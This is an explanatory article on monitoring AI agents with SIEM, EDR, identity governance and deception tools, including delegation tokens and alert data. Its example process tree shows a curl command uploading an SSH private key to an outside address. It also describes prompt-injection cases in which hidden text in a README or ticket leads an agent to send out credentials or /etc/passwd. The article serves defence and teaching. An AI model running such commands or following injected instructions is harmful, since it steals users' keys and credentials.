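# Complementary security tooling for AI agents: how SIEM, EDR, identity governance and deception platforms divide the work

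## What each of the four kinds of tool can see when an AI agent acts

An AI agent is a language model that other software, called the harness, runs in a loop and connects to tools such as a shell, a web browser or an API. The harness sends the model prompts, carries out the actions it requests and returns the results. Organisations use agents to write code, handle support requests and operate internal systems. An agent usually works with either an employee's permissions or its own account.

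Security teams mostly monitor AI agents with products that predate them, and each kind of product misses a different part of what an agent does. SIEM (security information and event management) platforms gather logs from many systems and correlate them into alerts. EDR (endpoint detection and response) software records what happens on a machine and can block it. Identity governance tools track accounts, who owns them and what they can access. Deception platforms plant fake assets and raise an alert when anyone touches one.

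Suppose an employee asks a coding agent on a laptop to summarise a support ticket. The agent fetches the ticket, reads the employee's private SSH key (a file that lets its holder log in to servers) and sends the key to an address outside the company. *ADR* (Li, Hu and colleagues, 2026), an account of the agent monitoring system that Uber built for itself, describes almost the same sequence. No step has to break an access rule, because the employee is allowed to read the key, the agent runs as the employee, and the laptop is allowed to open web connections. Monitoring agents is difficult mostly because an agent can have permission for an action that doesn't serve the user's purpose.

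### The path of one tool call

*Unrolling the Codex agent loop* (Bolin, 2026) describes how Codex CLI, OpenAI's command-line coding agent, handles a step like the one in which the agent reads the key. The harness first assembles a prompt containing general instructions, definitions of the available tools and a description of the working directory, followed by the user's request. The definition of the shell tool, for instance, lists a command, a working directory and a time limit as its parameters. The harness then sends the prompt to the model over the network.

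The model returns either a final answer or a tool call, which is a structured request for one action. In Bolin's example, the tool call contains the name of the shell tool, the command `cat README.md` and an identifier. A request to read a private key would differ only in the file path.

The harness, not the model, runs the command that opens the file. It labels the output with the same identifier, appends it to the prompt and queries the model again. This repeats until the model produces a message for the user, and a single request can involve hundreds of tool calls. If the model runs on a provider's servers, the key leaves the laptop in the next prompt after the agent reads it, before any attacker has received anything.

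The harness is the natural place to record all this, but how much it records depends on its settings. Anthropic's documentation for its coding agent, Claude Code, lists exportable events for each prompt, model request, permission decision and tool result, with an identifier that links the events from one prompt. By default, Claude Code redacts the prompt text and leaves out the shell command, so the reading of the key would appear only as a successful shell call, with its duration and the size of its output in bytes. If a setting, not a person, accepted the call, the event does not show which setting matched. An administrator has to turn on the fuller record.

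Below the harness, the operating system starts a shell process, opens the key file and later opens a network connection for the upload. Endpoint software can record each step with the time, user account and parent process, but encryption normally hides the data sent over the connection. If the harness uses a built-in file reader, no shell starts, and the harness's own process opens the key file. Some Claude Code sessions run in the cloud instead of on the user's device. These sessions cannot reach the key on the laptop, but they may contain other secrets, and the laptop's endpoint software does not record what happens to them.

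The remote services keep the last set of records. The harness fetches the ticket through a server that uses the Model Context Protocol (MCP), a common interface between agents and outside tools. That server calls the ticketing system, which can log which account requested which ticket. Bolin notes that the Codex sandbox covers only Codex's own shell tool, so MCP servers have to enforce their own limits. Whoever runs the address that receives the key holds its logs.

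The reason for the action is therefore in one log and its effect in another. *AgentSight* (Zheng, Yu and colleagues, 2025) calls this a semantic gap. A monitor inside the application shows that a script ran successfully, and a monitor on the operating system shows a shell writing to a file, but neither connects the two. The researchers' tool reads both the decrypted traffic to the model and the operating system's events. They tested it on an agent instructed to download and build a C project. The project's README pointed to a web page with a hidden prompt, and the agent read `/etc/passwd`, the list of accounts on a Unix machine, and sent it to a collection server. AgentSight captured 521 events and merged them into 37, and a second language model judged the agent's actions inconsistent with its stated goal. This single staged attack shows that joined records can expose the mismatch, but not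 how often such a judge would be wrong.

Delay can break the link between the harness log and system records, even when a tool collects both. In *AgentLoupe*, Bao, Liu and colleagues (2026) staged an attack in which an agent writes a malicious script and schedules it to run every hour. The system scheduler later starts the script in a process that has no parent-child link to the agent. The harness log shows the request and the job being installed, but nothing after that. A system monitor records the scheduler, the shell and the outgoing connection. Some research systems can also trace the files back to the agent's process, but not to the specific exchange with the model that produced them.

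AgentSight also fails here, because it follows only the agent's descendant processes and matches events within half a second of a model response. Bao and colleagues instead label the file itself, so the link remains after the delay. Their evidence is two case studies, and they acknowledge they have not measured how often the labels spread too far or go missing.

### Four questions that predate agents

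The evidence of an attack is usually scattered over many systems, so SIEM platforms look for events that seem unremarkable one by one but together amount to an incident. The Australian Signals Directorate's *Implementing SIEM and SOAR platforms* (2025) defines a SIEM as software or an appliance that collects, centralises and analyses logs for security purposes. A well-configured SIEM compares those logs with a baseline of normal activity and applies rules and filters. The guidance illustrates the main weakness with an organisation that forwards logs from only 10 of its 12 Active Directory servers, the machines that manage Windows accounts, which leaves its SIEM with a blind spot for whatever happens on the other two. An agent whose harness exports no logs creates the same kind of blind spot.

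EDR monitors individual machines for behaviour that resembles malware or an intruder. IBM's *What is endpoint detection and response (EDR)?* describes software that continuously collects data from laptops, servers and mobile devices, analyses it in real time for signs of known or suspected threats, and can respond automatically. This works best when harmful activity looks different from ordinary activity. That difference was already shrinking, for reasons that have little to do with AI agents. According to The Hacker News (2026), the security firm CrowdStrike found that 82 percent of its detections in 2025 involved no malware, as attackers moved through networks with valid credentials and trusted tools.

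Identity governance tracks which identities exist, who is responsible for each, what each may access and whether it still needs that access. It began as a way to keep staff access up to date as people joined, changed jobs and left, and was later extended to software accounts, which now include those of agents. An agent may also appear in identity records through an OAuth grant, which is a user's recorded consent for an application to act on their account. NHIMG, a publisher on the security of non-human identities, asserts that many teams discover agents only after such grants have widened the agents' access. NHIMG's claim is not a measurement, but it suggests that identity records of an agent may exist before anyone looks at them.

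Deception platforms mostly avoid the problem of judging ordinary activity. They plant servers, files and passwords that no legitimate task should need, then watch for anyone touching them. A canary credential, for example, is a fake key or password that raises an alert when anyone tries to use it. A lack of alerts is only weak evidence that nothing is wrong, because an agent can do a great deal of harm without touching a decoy.

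### Acalvio's division of the work

A table in Acalvio's *How to secure AI agents* (2026) lists a primary strength and a primary limitation for each of these four kinds of tool. The version below adds what each would record when the agent reads and sends the key. It also adds a row for the agent record, which is the log of prompts, tool calls and results kept by the harness or hooks inside it.

| Tool | Strength, per Acalvio | Limitation, per Acalvio | Record in the example |
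|---|---|---|---|
| SIEM | Event correlation | Depends on the available telemetry | Whichever of the other records reach it, joined by user, machine and time |
| EDR | Endpoint telemetry | Covers the endpoint only | A process belonging to the agent opened the key file and connected to an outside address |
| Identity governance | Control of access | Does not validate intent at runtime | The agent's identity, its owner and its valid access to the ticket |
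| Deception | Detection of misuse at runtime | Needs deliberate placement in the agent's way | Nothing, unless the key was a fake; then an alert when someone tries it |
| Agent record | Not in the table | Not in the table | The request, the ticket text and the calls that read and sent the key, if the settings keep them |

Acalvio sells deception products, and its original table reflects that. Three columns name general classes of tool, while the fourth names Acalvio's own product, 360 Deception. The limitation listed for deception is a matter of installation, which a customer can fix by placing more decoys, whereas the one listed for identity governance is something the tool cannot establish at all.

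Contact with a decoy is good evidence that an agent has strayed from its task, but it doesn't show whether the cause was a hidden instruction, a clumsy search or an intruder. Acalvio's further claim that deception "validates" an agent's intent therefore goes too far.

The entries for SIEM and EDR are better supported, by organisations that were not selling either product. The Australian guidance makes the same point about missing log sources. Li and colleagues are more specific than Acalvio about EDR. They write that EDR records that an agent wrote a file, but not the prompt, reasoning or tool calls that led to the write. Later sections test the table's claims one tool at a time, against measurements where these exist.

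### Three explanations for the same action

The example so far doesn't explain why the agent read the key. The ticket may have contained an instruction to do so. That would be prompt injection, in which an agent wrongly follows text it reads as a command. Shteinberg (2026) points out on Microsoft's community site that agents act on whatever content they take in, much of which the user doesn't control.

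In a controlled test, Li and colleagues reproduced an attack of this type that the security firm Zenity had published as AgentFlayer. A malicious email automatically created a ticket containing hidden instructions in Jira, a widely used tracking system. When the user's coding tool fetched the ticket over MCP, the agent read local configuration files and sent credentials out over the web. Uber's monitor flagged the injection, the access to credentials and the outbound transfer. The attacker needed only to send an email, without an account inside the company or malware on the laptop.

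There may also be no attacker. Suppose the ticket reports a failed login, and the agent reads the key to reproduce the fault, then uploads it to an online diagnostic service. The organisation's own agent has overreached while working on a genuine request. Uber's deployment offers partial evidence that secrets leak without malice. Li and colleagues report that hundreds of credentials, in 26 categories, inadvertently left the company's network. These are not clear cases of overreach, though, because Uber responded with a filter that scans prompts before they reach the agent, which suggests that people had typed or pasted at least some of the secrets themselves.

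The agent may also belong to an intruder. Sophos' *AI Security 2026* (2026) reports that in May 2026 the security company found an attacker running around a dozen agents inside a customer's network. The agents, each on its own virtual machine, wrote malware and tested it against three endpoint protection products, producing nearly 80 modules and more than 70 evasion techniques. The same operator later used the results to deploy ransomware and steal data. A defender would normally have no agent record to consult then, because the attacker controls the harness. The attacker, or perhaps the company that supplies the model, holds any log that exists.

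On the endpoint, benign, hijacked and attacker-run agents can look much the same. The Hacker News lists requests for credentials stored in browsers, downloads through legitimate system programs and changes to what runs at startup among the actions all three now take. Sophos (2026) likewise finds in its own Windows telemetry that some harmless agent activity is indistinguishable from what an active adversary might do. In IT Brew's *Telling the difference between an attacker and an internal AI agent*, Jon Baker of the security firm AttackIQ says that an outsider's agent might behave much like an internal one pushing against its guardrails. He suggests looking at what happened before and after the attempted access.

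The company has to replace the key whichever explanation is right, but the rest of the response differs. After an injection, the team needs to find the ticket and every other agent that has read it. After overreach, it needs to narrow the agent's access or improve its instructions. If there is an intruder, it has to remove them from the network. The team can use the ticket to tell injection from overreach if the agent record kept its text. To recognise an intruder's agent, it needs a reliable list of the organisation's own agents.

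## Finding the agents and giving each an identity, an owner and limits

To keep a reliable list of its agents, an organisation has to find them, register each with an owner and a purpose, issue each a credential, grant access, review that access and eventually revoke it. For staff, a hiring record starts this process, but an agent can begin work without one. The Cloud Security Alliance, an industry body, warns that nobody offboards agents either, so they keep their access after they have served their purpose.

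### Discovering agents

Some agents appear in records the organisation already keeps. Identity systems list OAuth grants, cloud platforms list service accounts, and device management lists installed products. Many coding agents also store configuration files in the user's profile that name their MCP servers, and these files can be found even when the agent isn't running. But a home-made script of a few dozen lines that calls a model and runs its output in a shell has no installer and may not appear in any of these places.

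Such scripts are hard to identify by their behaviour. An agent typically holds a connection to a remote service and runs commands, but so does `npm install`, which developers run all day. Canale and Soulis (2026) argue in *Detecting Shadow AI* that every agent has a "behavioural twin", the same program talking to a service that isn't AI. A rule based only on the structure of processes and connections cannot separate the two.

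Their open-source Windows program, Agent Detector, therefore first looks for signs that a process is communicating with a model, mainly by checking its connections against a catalogue of 184 model service entries. It only then checks whether that process has started a shell. It also searches installed software, configuration and traces of past execution for 39 known tools. It never reads prompts or file contents.

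Canale and Soulis tested the detector on one laptop with 12 synthetic agents, 3 AI components that aren't agents (such as an MCP server running alone) and 9 harmless workloads, including three "behavioural twins" that act like agents. Most of the synthetic agents polled a real model service with an invalid key and sent harmless commands to a shell. They ran the whole set five times with ordinary user rights, and the detector scanned each episode three times within about half a minute. It found all 12 agents in most runs and flagged none of the harmless workloads. Two simple behavioural rules each flagged four of the nine harmless workloads, including all three twins, and missed two or three agents.

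The detector found ten of the agents in all five runs and the other two in only three. Timing caused both failures.

One of the two was a Python agent connected to OpenAI's API. OpenAI's service sits behind a content delivery network that uses the same addresses for unrelated websites, so the address alone doesn't identify it. The detector has to look up the matching name in the Windows DNS cache, which temporarily stores recent name lookups. OpenAI's entries last at most 60 seconds. When the agent received an entry that was close to expiring, the entry expired before the first scan, 8.6 seconds after the agent started.

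The other agent called Anthropic's API every ten seconds and closed its connection five seconds after each call. Because the scans happened at almost the same times in every run, detection depended on whether the third scan began just before or just after a connection closed. With administrator rights, the detector missed this agent in all five runs. Canale and Soulis then scanned it 40 times at random intervals and found it in 15 of those scans.

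The result of 12 out of 12 overstates the detector's accuracy, as the researchers acknowledge. They had corrected two rules after seeing errors on the same test bench, so five of the episodes were no longer independent tests. Every scan also came within seconds of the agent starting, whereas the deployed version scans once an hour. When the researchers kept connections open to four providers behind shared networks, the detector could attribute none of them after 295 seconds, although all the agents were still connected. It also missed an agent that used an unlisted relay, one that ran for only five seconds, and one inside WSL 2, the Linux environment in Windows. It cannot detect agents that run in a provider's cloud.

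A scan that finds no agents on a laptop is weak evidence that there are none. The detector writes a summary event each time it runs, so if a machine stops sending these events, someone has removed the detector or it has broken. Agents that the scans miss tend to show up elsewhere, for example through a bill from a model provider or an OAuth grant that matches no known agent.

### Registering an owner and a purpose

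After a scan finds a program, someone still has to establish who is responsible for it and what it is for. Canale and Soulis cite a study of 27 unapproved systems in which organisations phased out the systems they found, replaced them or kept them under management. Organisations have the same options when they find an agent. As a first step, Agent Detector shows the user a notice about unapproved tools and prompts them to acknowledge it. The acknowledgement does not prove that anyone read the notice, because any process running as the user, including the agent, can write the same event.

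A useful register entry names a person as owner, describes the task in a sentence, and records where the agent runs, which model, tools and data it uses, and when its approval ends. These fields have no settled standard. In *Accelerating the Adoption of Software and AI Agent Identity and Authorization*, a concept paper from the US National Institute of Standards and Technology (NIST), Booth, Fisher and colleagues (2026) ask which metadata an agent's identity needs and whether it should be fixed or last only for one task. For now, it makes sense to keep the register entry for as long as the agent exists and issue credentials for each task.

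Register entries are often too vague to be useful. A reviewer can check an agent's access against "summarises support tickets for the support team", but not against "productivity assistant". Entries also go out of date. Comparing the register with the staff directory shows which agents have owners who have left, and comparing it with discovery results shows which agents nobody registered.

### Choosing whose account the agent uses

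We'll call the employee in the running example Dana. The account her agent uses strongly affects how much damage it can do and how clear the record is afterwards.

| How the agent runs | What a service's log shows | What the agent can reach | What disabling the account interrupts |
|---|---|---|---|
| Under Dana's account | Dana, whether she or the agent acted | Everything Dana can reach, including her key | Dana's own work |
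| Under a shared service account | The shared account, with no sign of which program or person was behind it | Whatever any program on that account needs | Every program on that account |
| Under its own identity, with delegation from Dana | Both Dana and the agent, if the service records both | The part of Dana's access passed to it | That agent |

Running the agent as Dana takes the least effort, and many developers prefer to work locally. But an agent running as Dana has all her access and can impersonate her, as NIST's August 2026 post *Back to the Future* points out. The post predicts that local agents will persist and recommends a hardened harness or a sandbox that limits what the agent can access.

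A shared service account often looks tidier because it separates the agent from any employee, but it can be the worst of the three. Bradshaw (2026), in *An AI Agent Is Not a Service Account*, imagines a procurement agent that a team hurriedly launches on an existing account with broad purchasing rights. The agent has long-lived credentials and no named sponsor. Two weeks later, auditors find orders beyond its authority and changed bank details for suppliers. The incident is hypothetical, so it isn't evidence of how often such failures happen.

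An agent with its own identity needs its own credential, and teams in a hurry tend to use an API key, a fixed string that the agent presents with each request. The key doesn't prove who is using it, so anyone who copies it can use it too. NIST notes that keys are often left unprotected in configuration files and logs. Short-lived credentials limit how long a copy is useful, and SPIFFE, a framework for giving running programs cryptographic identities, is one way to issue them. DPoP ties a token to a private key that the caller must prove it holds, so a copied token doesn't work without that key.

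Signs of credential problems include the same credential in use from two machines at once, a key that hasn't changed since a pilot project, and a secret in a log file. NIST (2026) finalised its guidelines on protecting tokens from misuse in September.

### A token that names both the user and the agent

Delegation means that Dana passes limited authority to the agent and the record keeps both names. Infosys' *Enterprise AI identity and access architecture* lists token exchange as one way to do this for company agents. The token exchange standard, RFC 8693, dates from 2020 and was not written for AI agents. Its `act` claim is a token field that identifies the party acting on the user's behalf.

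The exchange starts with two tokens, one that represents Dana and one that represents the agent. The agent's software sends both to the company's authorisation server, along with the name of the service it wants to reach and the permissions it wants. If company policy allows the combination, the server signs and returns a new token. Its contents might look like this:

```json
{
  "iss": "company-login",
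  "sub": "dana",
  "aud": "ticket-system",
  "scope": "tickets:read attachments:read",
  "iat": 1794830400,
  "exp": 1794831000,
  "act": { "sub": "ticket-summariser" }
}
```

The `sub` field identifies Dana, whose authority the agent is using, and the `sub` inside `act` identifies the agent. The `aud` field restricts the token to the ticketing system, and `scope` restricts it to reading tickets and attachments. The two numbers are the issue and expiry times in seconds, ten minutes apart. When the agent makes a request, the ticketing system verifies the signature and checks these fields. It should then log both names so an investigator can tell Dana's own actions from the agent's.

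Suppose the ticket has a long attachment, and the summariser hands it to a second agent that only reads documents. The second agent doesn't need the summariser's token. The authorisation server can issue another, with fewer permissions and a shorter life:

| Holder | Identities in the token | Permitted actions | Lifetime |
|---|---|---|---|
| Dana's own session | Dana | Read and edit tickets, read attachments, export reports | 8 hours |
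| Ticket summariser | Dana; summariser acting | Read tickets and attachments | 10 minutes |
| Attachment reader | Dana; attachment reader acting, summariser before it | Read attachments | 2 minutes |

In the last token, the attachment reader's `act` field contains another `act` field for the summariser, which preserves the chain of delegation. Under RFC 8693, the earlier links are for information only, and a service bases its decision on the current actor and the token's main fields. The chain is therefore more useful for investigating an agent's actions than for limiting them.

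The standard also doesn't require authority to shrink at each handoff. The authorisation server has to enforce that, and a careless policy could give the attachment reader more authority than the summariser had. Some designs build the restriction into the token itself. *Rethinking Access Control for AI Agents* (Zhou and Zhang, 2026), a survey of recent research, describes a system that uses Macaroons, which are tokens that let a holder add restrictions and use cryptography to prevent later holders from removing them.

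Delegation has failed if a service's logs show a known agent's traffic under Dana's name with no `act` field, which suggests that the agent is using Dana's own token. Other clear signs are a child token with wider permissions than its parent and a token that several unrelated services accept.

### Deciding who should have access and whether a request passes

In identity governance, people decide who should have access. They do this over days or weeks and record the result, for example that the ticket summariser may read tickets for support staff until the end of March. At runtime, software determines within milliseconds whether to allow each request, using the token, the resource and the policy in force. This check can run in the service itself or in a separate policy system, which the service can call through the common interface defined by the AuthZEN specification.

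Access reviews and runtime checks can each fail while the other works. If the ticketing system ignores the `scope` field, the access review will find no problem even though the agent is editing tickets. A successful edit under a read-only token is evidence of this failure. If the support team stops using the summariser and nobody removes its access, every runtime check will correctly enforce a permission that should no longer exist. No individual request will look wrong, so only a review can find the problem.

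### A valid token and the wrong purpose

Delegation tokens wouldn't have protected Dana's SSH key, because the operating system doesn't require one when a program opens a local file. Separating the agent from the user, by running it in an account or container that cannot read the key, would have prevented the theft in the original example.

A hidden instruction can instead exploit access the agent legitimately has. Suppose Dana asks the agent to summarise ticket 4711 and post the summary as a reply, and the agent's token lets it read and answer any support ticket. The ticket contains a hidden instruction to open another customer's ticket and paste its contents into the reply. The token is genuine and current, and its scope covers both actions. The log correctly names Dana and the agent. The token doesn't record that Dana wanted a summary of only one ticket, so the ticketing system has no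 basis for refusing the requests.

Zhou and Zhang argue that each step across the boundaries between systems needs its own decision, because permission to read a document need not include permission to send it anywhere. In this case, though, the agent has both permissions because the task needs both.

A supporter of delegation can fairly reply that the scope was too broad. FedScoop's *The zero-trust controls federal agencies need for autonomous AI* argues that authority should match the task, the resource and the time needed. An OAuth extension called Rich Authorization Requests can express such limits. For example, a token could allow the agent only to read and reply to ticket 4711, for ten minutes. The attack then fails when the agent tries to open the other customer's ticket, even if the agent is completely fooled.

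Limiting an agent's access to what its task requires depends on someone knowing those requirements in advance. That is easy for "summarise ticket 4711", but "find out why this customer can't log in" may require other tickets, server logs and source code, and the agent may not discover which until it has started. Zhou and Zhang identify this lack of a complete plan as a basic difficulty of agent access control, and the NIST concept paper asks how to establish least privilege when nobody can fully predict an agent's actions. A broad grant gives the agent more access than it needs, while a narrow one means that it keeps asking for more.

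People need to consider those requests carefully, but NIST warns of consent fatigue, in which they click "allow" out of habit to keep the work moving. SpruceID, a digital identity company that commented on the concept paper, proposes that each request for extra access should be understandable on its own, so that someone can review it later. That would help a careful reviewer, but it doesn't reduce the number of requests.

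Software could choose the scope instead. Zhou and Zhang describe research systems that match permissions to the meaning of the task, and note that these systems may depend on a model to choose the permissions. The cryptography can then guarantee that nobody expands the chosen scope, but not that the model chose well.

Even a perfectly scoped agent can misuse its permissions. If ticket 4711 contains an internal note or a password, the agent can copy it into the reply using only the permissions it needs for the summary. Restricting the reply to an approved recipient doesn't help if that recipient shouldn't see the note. To catch this, a tool has to check the content or check whether the action fits the task, which is intent validation.

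Per-task scopes are therefore most useful for narrow, repetitive jobs and leave the largest gap when the task is open-ended. Zhou and Zhang argue that evaluations should examine both what an agent did and what unauthorised effects it could still produce. A team can test its own agents this way by listing everything a token would let an agent do if it followed a hostile instruction.

### Reviewing and revoking access

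Quarterly reviews are a poor fit for agents. The Cloud Security Alliance says that many enterprises have more than 50 non-human identities, which include service accounts and agents, for every human one, and that their number grows daily. It gives no measurement to support that ratio, but even if the ratio were much lower, reviewers would be approving lists too long to read properly.

Expiry dates reduce the review work, because access ends unless the owner renews it. Changes such as a new owner, MCP server or task should also trigger a review. At each review, the owner can compare the permissions granted with those the agent has used. The agent may still need an unused permission for a rare task, but the owner should be able to explain why. Hundreds of approvals within a few minutes suggest that nobody is reviewing them.

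To revoke an agent's access, the team first stops the harness, then disables the agent's identity and withdraws its OAuth grants so that it cannot obtain new tokens. Tokens already issued may still work. A service that checks only the signature and expiry time will accept the summariser's token until its ten-minute lifetime ends, which is a strong reason to keep lifetimes short. The team also has to replace any fixed secrets the agent has read, such as Dana's key.

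Work the agent has already started can continue. Zhou and Zhang point out that a second agent may keep running after the first has changed its plan, and that a stored result can outlast access to its source. The hourly script that Bao and colleagues had an agent install would also keep running after the team disabled the agent's identity.

Sharing agents makes revocation harder still. If the attachment reader serves both the ticket summariser and a contracts agent, revoking the summariser shouldn't stop the contracts work. Zhou and Zhang describe VERA, a research system that records delegations as a graph and revokes individual links. An agent keeps its access while at least one independent, authorised path to it remains. A company without such a system can still record who delegated what to whom, then trace the links by hand.

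A May 2026 NIST workshop with more than 400 participants also raised the difficulty of containing an agent that has access to several connected services. Isolating one machine may not be enough, according to ExecutiveGov's *NIST Identifies AI Incident Response and Security Gaps*. The workshop report lists credential revocation among the areas that need more attention. A team can test its own procedure by revoking a harmless agent and searching every connected service for later activity under its name. If a request succeeds after the last token should have expired, the team has missed a credential, a grant or a service. The team can then use the same procedure when revocation follows an alert rather than a review.

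### Where the NIST project stands

Most of the components described here already exist as standards or products, but companies lack a tested example of how to combine them for agents. The National Cybersecurity Center of Excellence (NCCoE), part of NIST, plans to provide one. In its February 2026 concept paper, Booth and colleagues proposed a project on identifying agents, authorising them, linking them to users and logging what they do. They limited the first phase to agents inside enterprises and excluded agents from untrusted outside sources. The candidate standards include OAuth, SPIFFE and SCIM, which automates the creation and removal of accounts across systems.

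The paper drew over 600 formal responses, according to *Advancing Standards for Agent Identity* (Galluzzo, 2026), the description of a conference session scheduled for 10 November. Responses to a separate NIST request about securing agents make similar points. *Securing AI Agents NIST RFI Filings March 2026* (Technology Policy Institute, 2026) lists Okta, Cloudflare and the OpenID Foundation among those calling for unique agent credentials, scoped permissions and revocation at machine speed. It also reports a consensus that NIST's existing digital identity guidelines are the right foundation but incomplete for agents. Some of these respondents, including Okta, sell identity products and stand to gain from such requirements.

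NIST followed in October with ten principles, in Booth's *Design Tenets for Agent Identity Management Systems* (2026). According to Biometric Update's *NIST sets 10 principles for AI agent identity and authorization*, each agent should have its own accountable identity, traceable to whoever launched it. Its access should be minimal, temporary and revocable, and it should have a log that it cannot alter. The principles also separate what an agent may do from what it decides to try. NIST acknowledges that current standards and technology don't fully meet all ten.

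The project is still at an early stage. NCCoE's project page, *Software and SI Agent Identity and Authorization*, lists its status as "Soliciting Comments" and offers a summary of the responses and an online resource hub. NCCoE now takes feedback on a rolling basis. It plans to publish a practice guide with example architectures and build details from its laboratory. Until the guide appears, a company has to design and test its own combination.

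The page's title uses "SI agents" for what the concept paper called AI agents. SI stands for "super intelligence". ExecutiveGov's *NIST, NSA, CISA Issue AI Incident Response Practices* reports that a recent executive order requires federal agencies to use that term in official communications. The project's subject hasn't changed, but anyone searching for its documents will need both terms.

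## Watching and blocking agent activity on the endpoint

Delegation tokens can't protect Dana's SSH key, but EDR software on her laptop can record the agent opening it and may be able to block the access. However, coding agents routinely do many things that endpoint rules treat as signs of an attack, so a security team has to decide which alerts still matter.

### How EDR turns events into alerts

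Programs must send a request to the operating system's kernel to start a process, open a file or make a network connection. An EDR sensor records these requests as they happen, along with the time, user account, command line and requesting process. The sensor doesn't rely on the agent's harness for this record, so a hidden instruction that causes the agent to change its own logging settings doesn't affect the record. An agent with administrator rights could still try to switch the sensor off.

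In *AI coding agents are running on your machines*, Hernández and Lo Prete (2026) recorded Claude Code, Gemini CLI and Codex CLI at the kernel level for the security company Sysdig. In one session, the agent repeated its loop five times in ten seconds, each time starting a shell that ran a single command and exited. The developer saw one response, but the kernel logged 64 program launches. Canale and Soulis also note that real agents often start a new process for each command. A sensor that records every launch should catch these processes even if a periodic scan misses them.

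For Dana's agent, the record might look like this:

```text
terminal
└─ agent harness
   ├─ zsh
   │  └─ cat ~/.ssh/id_ed25519
   │       opens the key file
   └─ zsh
      └─ curl -F file=@/Users/dana/.ssh/id_ed25519 203.0.113.7
           opens the key file, connects to 203.0.113.7
```

Every process here runs under Dana's account, and `cat` and `curl` are ordinary programs. Only the process lineage, the chain of parent and child processes, connects them to the agent. The sensor can also record the command line, which includes the name of the file that `curl` sent, even if encryption hides the upload.

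Lineage helps only if the software can recognise the agent at the top of the chain. Hernández and Lo Prete found that Codex CLI runs as its own program and Claude Code as a bundled copy of Bun, a JavaScript runtime. Gemini CLI runs as a script inside the computer's shared copy of Node.js, so a rule that looks for a process called `gemini-cli` may miss it because the process appears as `node`, which also runs plenty of other software. The number of products makes recognising agents harder. Techzine's *CrowdStrike Falcon Update Makes the Endpoint the Hub for AI Security* reports that CrowdStrike detects more than 1,800 AI applications on its customers' devices, although many of these won't be agents.

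EDR software compares the recorded events with behavioural rules, which describe suspicious actions instead of known malicious files. A blocking rule stops the action, while a silent rule only records the match so that analysts or other rules can combine it with later events. A mistaken block interrupts someone's work, so blocking rules should be more reliable than silent ones.

Small details of a rule can determine whether it catches the theft of Dana's key. Elastic, which sells both SIEM and endpoint software, publishes a rule called *GenAI Process Accessing Sensitive Files*. The rule raises an alert when a process with the name of a known AI tool opens, creates or changes a sensitive file. In the tree above, `cat` and `curl` open the key, so the process name doesn't match. The name would match if the agent used its built-in file reader, but the query's file list leaves out SSH private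 keys, even though the rule's description mentions them. On Linux, the rule also receives no events when a program only reads a file.

The rule also searches collected events every five minutes, so it can report a theft but not prevent one. Another Elastic rule, "Credential Access via GenAI Tool Descendant", appears from its title to cover child processes. A team can check its own coverage by putting a dummy key on a test machine and having the agent read it both through a shell and with the built-in reader.

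### One week of alerts at Sophos

Sophos' *When AI agents look like attackers* examines seven days of rule hits from June 2026, recorded by the behavioural engine in the company's Windows product and limited to activity that AI agents had started. Most of the rule-hit categories come from MITRE ATT&CK, a public catalogue of attackers' methods. Sophos counted unique machines in each category, so a laptop with a hundred hits counts the same as a laptop with one.

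| Category | What the rules look for | Share of blocking hits | Share of silent hits |
|---|---|---|---|
| Credential access | Attempts to obtain passwords, keys or saved logins | 56.2% | 10% or less |
| Execution | Suspicious ways of running code | 28.8% | 11.1% |
| Evasion | Attempts to avoid security tools | 4.1% or less | 38.5% |
| Command and control | Communication that could let an outsider direct the machine | 4.1% or less | 34.0% |
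| Disrupt (Sophos' own category) | Activity stopped by its adaptive protection feature | 4.1% | 10% or less |

The silent hits reflect normal agent behavior. Agents make network calls, start child processes and write command lines that resemble those of attackers. All the Disrupt cases Sophos examined involved programs with low reputation scores, and none appeared malicious. Sophos doesn't identify the programs, but they could have been newly compiled code, which would score low because hardly anyone else has run it.

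A rule against decrypting saved browser data accounted for 42.6 percent of the blocking hits for credential access. One cause was GStack, a widely used pack of skills for coding agents. Its browsing skill started PowerShell, the Windows command shell, which decrypted browser data so that Claude Code could automate a browser session. Sophos considers this almost certainly benign but says the rule was right to fire, because stealing browser logins involves the same step.

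In another case, Claude closed a series of browser processes and ran a Python script that read the browser's stored credentials. It also listed the entries in Windows Credential Manager. Someone had started the session with a flag that turns off permission prompts. Sophos doesn't establish what the task was, but says that listing the Credential Manager entries would be enough on its own to bring in an analyst.

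The execution hits include a clearer example of harmless work. OpenAI's Codex tried to download a Python installer from the official site with `certutil`, a Windows certificate tool that attackers often use for downloads, and Sophos blocked it. The agent tried again a second later with a different output path, then several more times ten minutes later. Three seconds after the last attempt, it switched to `bitsadmin`, another built-in tool, which Sophos also blocked. Changing methods after a failure used to help distinguish a human attacker from a simple script, but agents now do it routinely.

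An older Sophos rule looked for PowerShell text formatting that attackers used to disguise commands. More than five years after Sophos wrote the rule, agents began producing similar formatting, and Sophos has since narrowed it. Sophos also blocked Cursor, an AI code editor, from placing a script in the Windows startup folder. The file name appeared to refer to an application called EZConvert, but Sophos couldn't confirm the script's purpose.

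These percentages don't show how often agents cause trouble. Sophos doesn't say how many machines ran agents, so the 56.2 percent is not the share of agents, or of machines with agents, that tried to reach credentials. It also depends on which rules Sophos has set to block, so a vendor with different rules would get a different figure from the same machines.

The rounding suggests that the blocking figures come from few machines. The smallest total that gives shares of 56.2, 28.8 and 4.1 percent is 73, with counts of 41, 21 and 3. The shares for the four credential rules fit a total of 47. Multiples of these totals would also fit, and Sophos publishes neither total. The company calls the analysis a "first-pass, short signal dump".

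Sophos also gives no false-positive rate. *When the Whole Company Adopts AI* (Fishbein, 2026) provides a partial substitute, using data from Intezer, which sells automated alert triage. About 73,000 of the 16.9 million alerts in the data related to AI. Intezer classed 94.1 percent of these as noise, 5.8 percent as genuine risks without a compromise, and 0.02 percent, or roughly 15 alerts, as real attacks. None of the confirmed attacks came from an organisation's own agent. Among the noisiest detections, between 77 and 99 percent of alerts were benign.

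Intezer's data include email and cloud alerts as well as endpoint alerts, and the company classified the alerts itself. The figures show how often an alert about AI turned out to be harmless, but not how often an agent's ordinary work triggers one or how many attacks raised no alert.

### Deciding what to exempt

Ignoring everything an agent does would be risky, even though few of the alerts are real attacks. An analyst who closed all 73,000 alerts unread would have missed about 15 attacks and some 4,200 alerts about genuine risks, such as an AI code editor opening a tunnel from a laptop to the public internet.

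A team can exempt the whole agent, exempt one known behaviour, or keep blocking an action whoever performs it. Exempting the agent means ignoring alerts from every process it starts. That may suit a disposable test machine with no secrets and little network access, but it rarely suits a developer's laptop. If the agent reads a ticket that contains a hidden instruction, the team will also ignore alerts about whatever the agent does in response.

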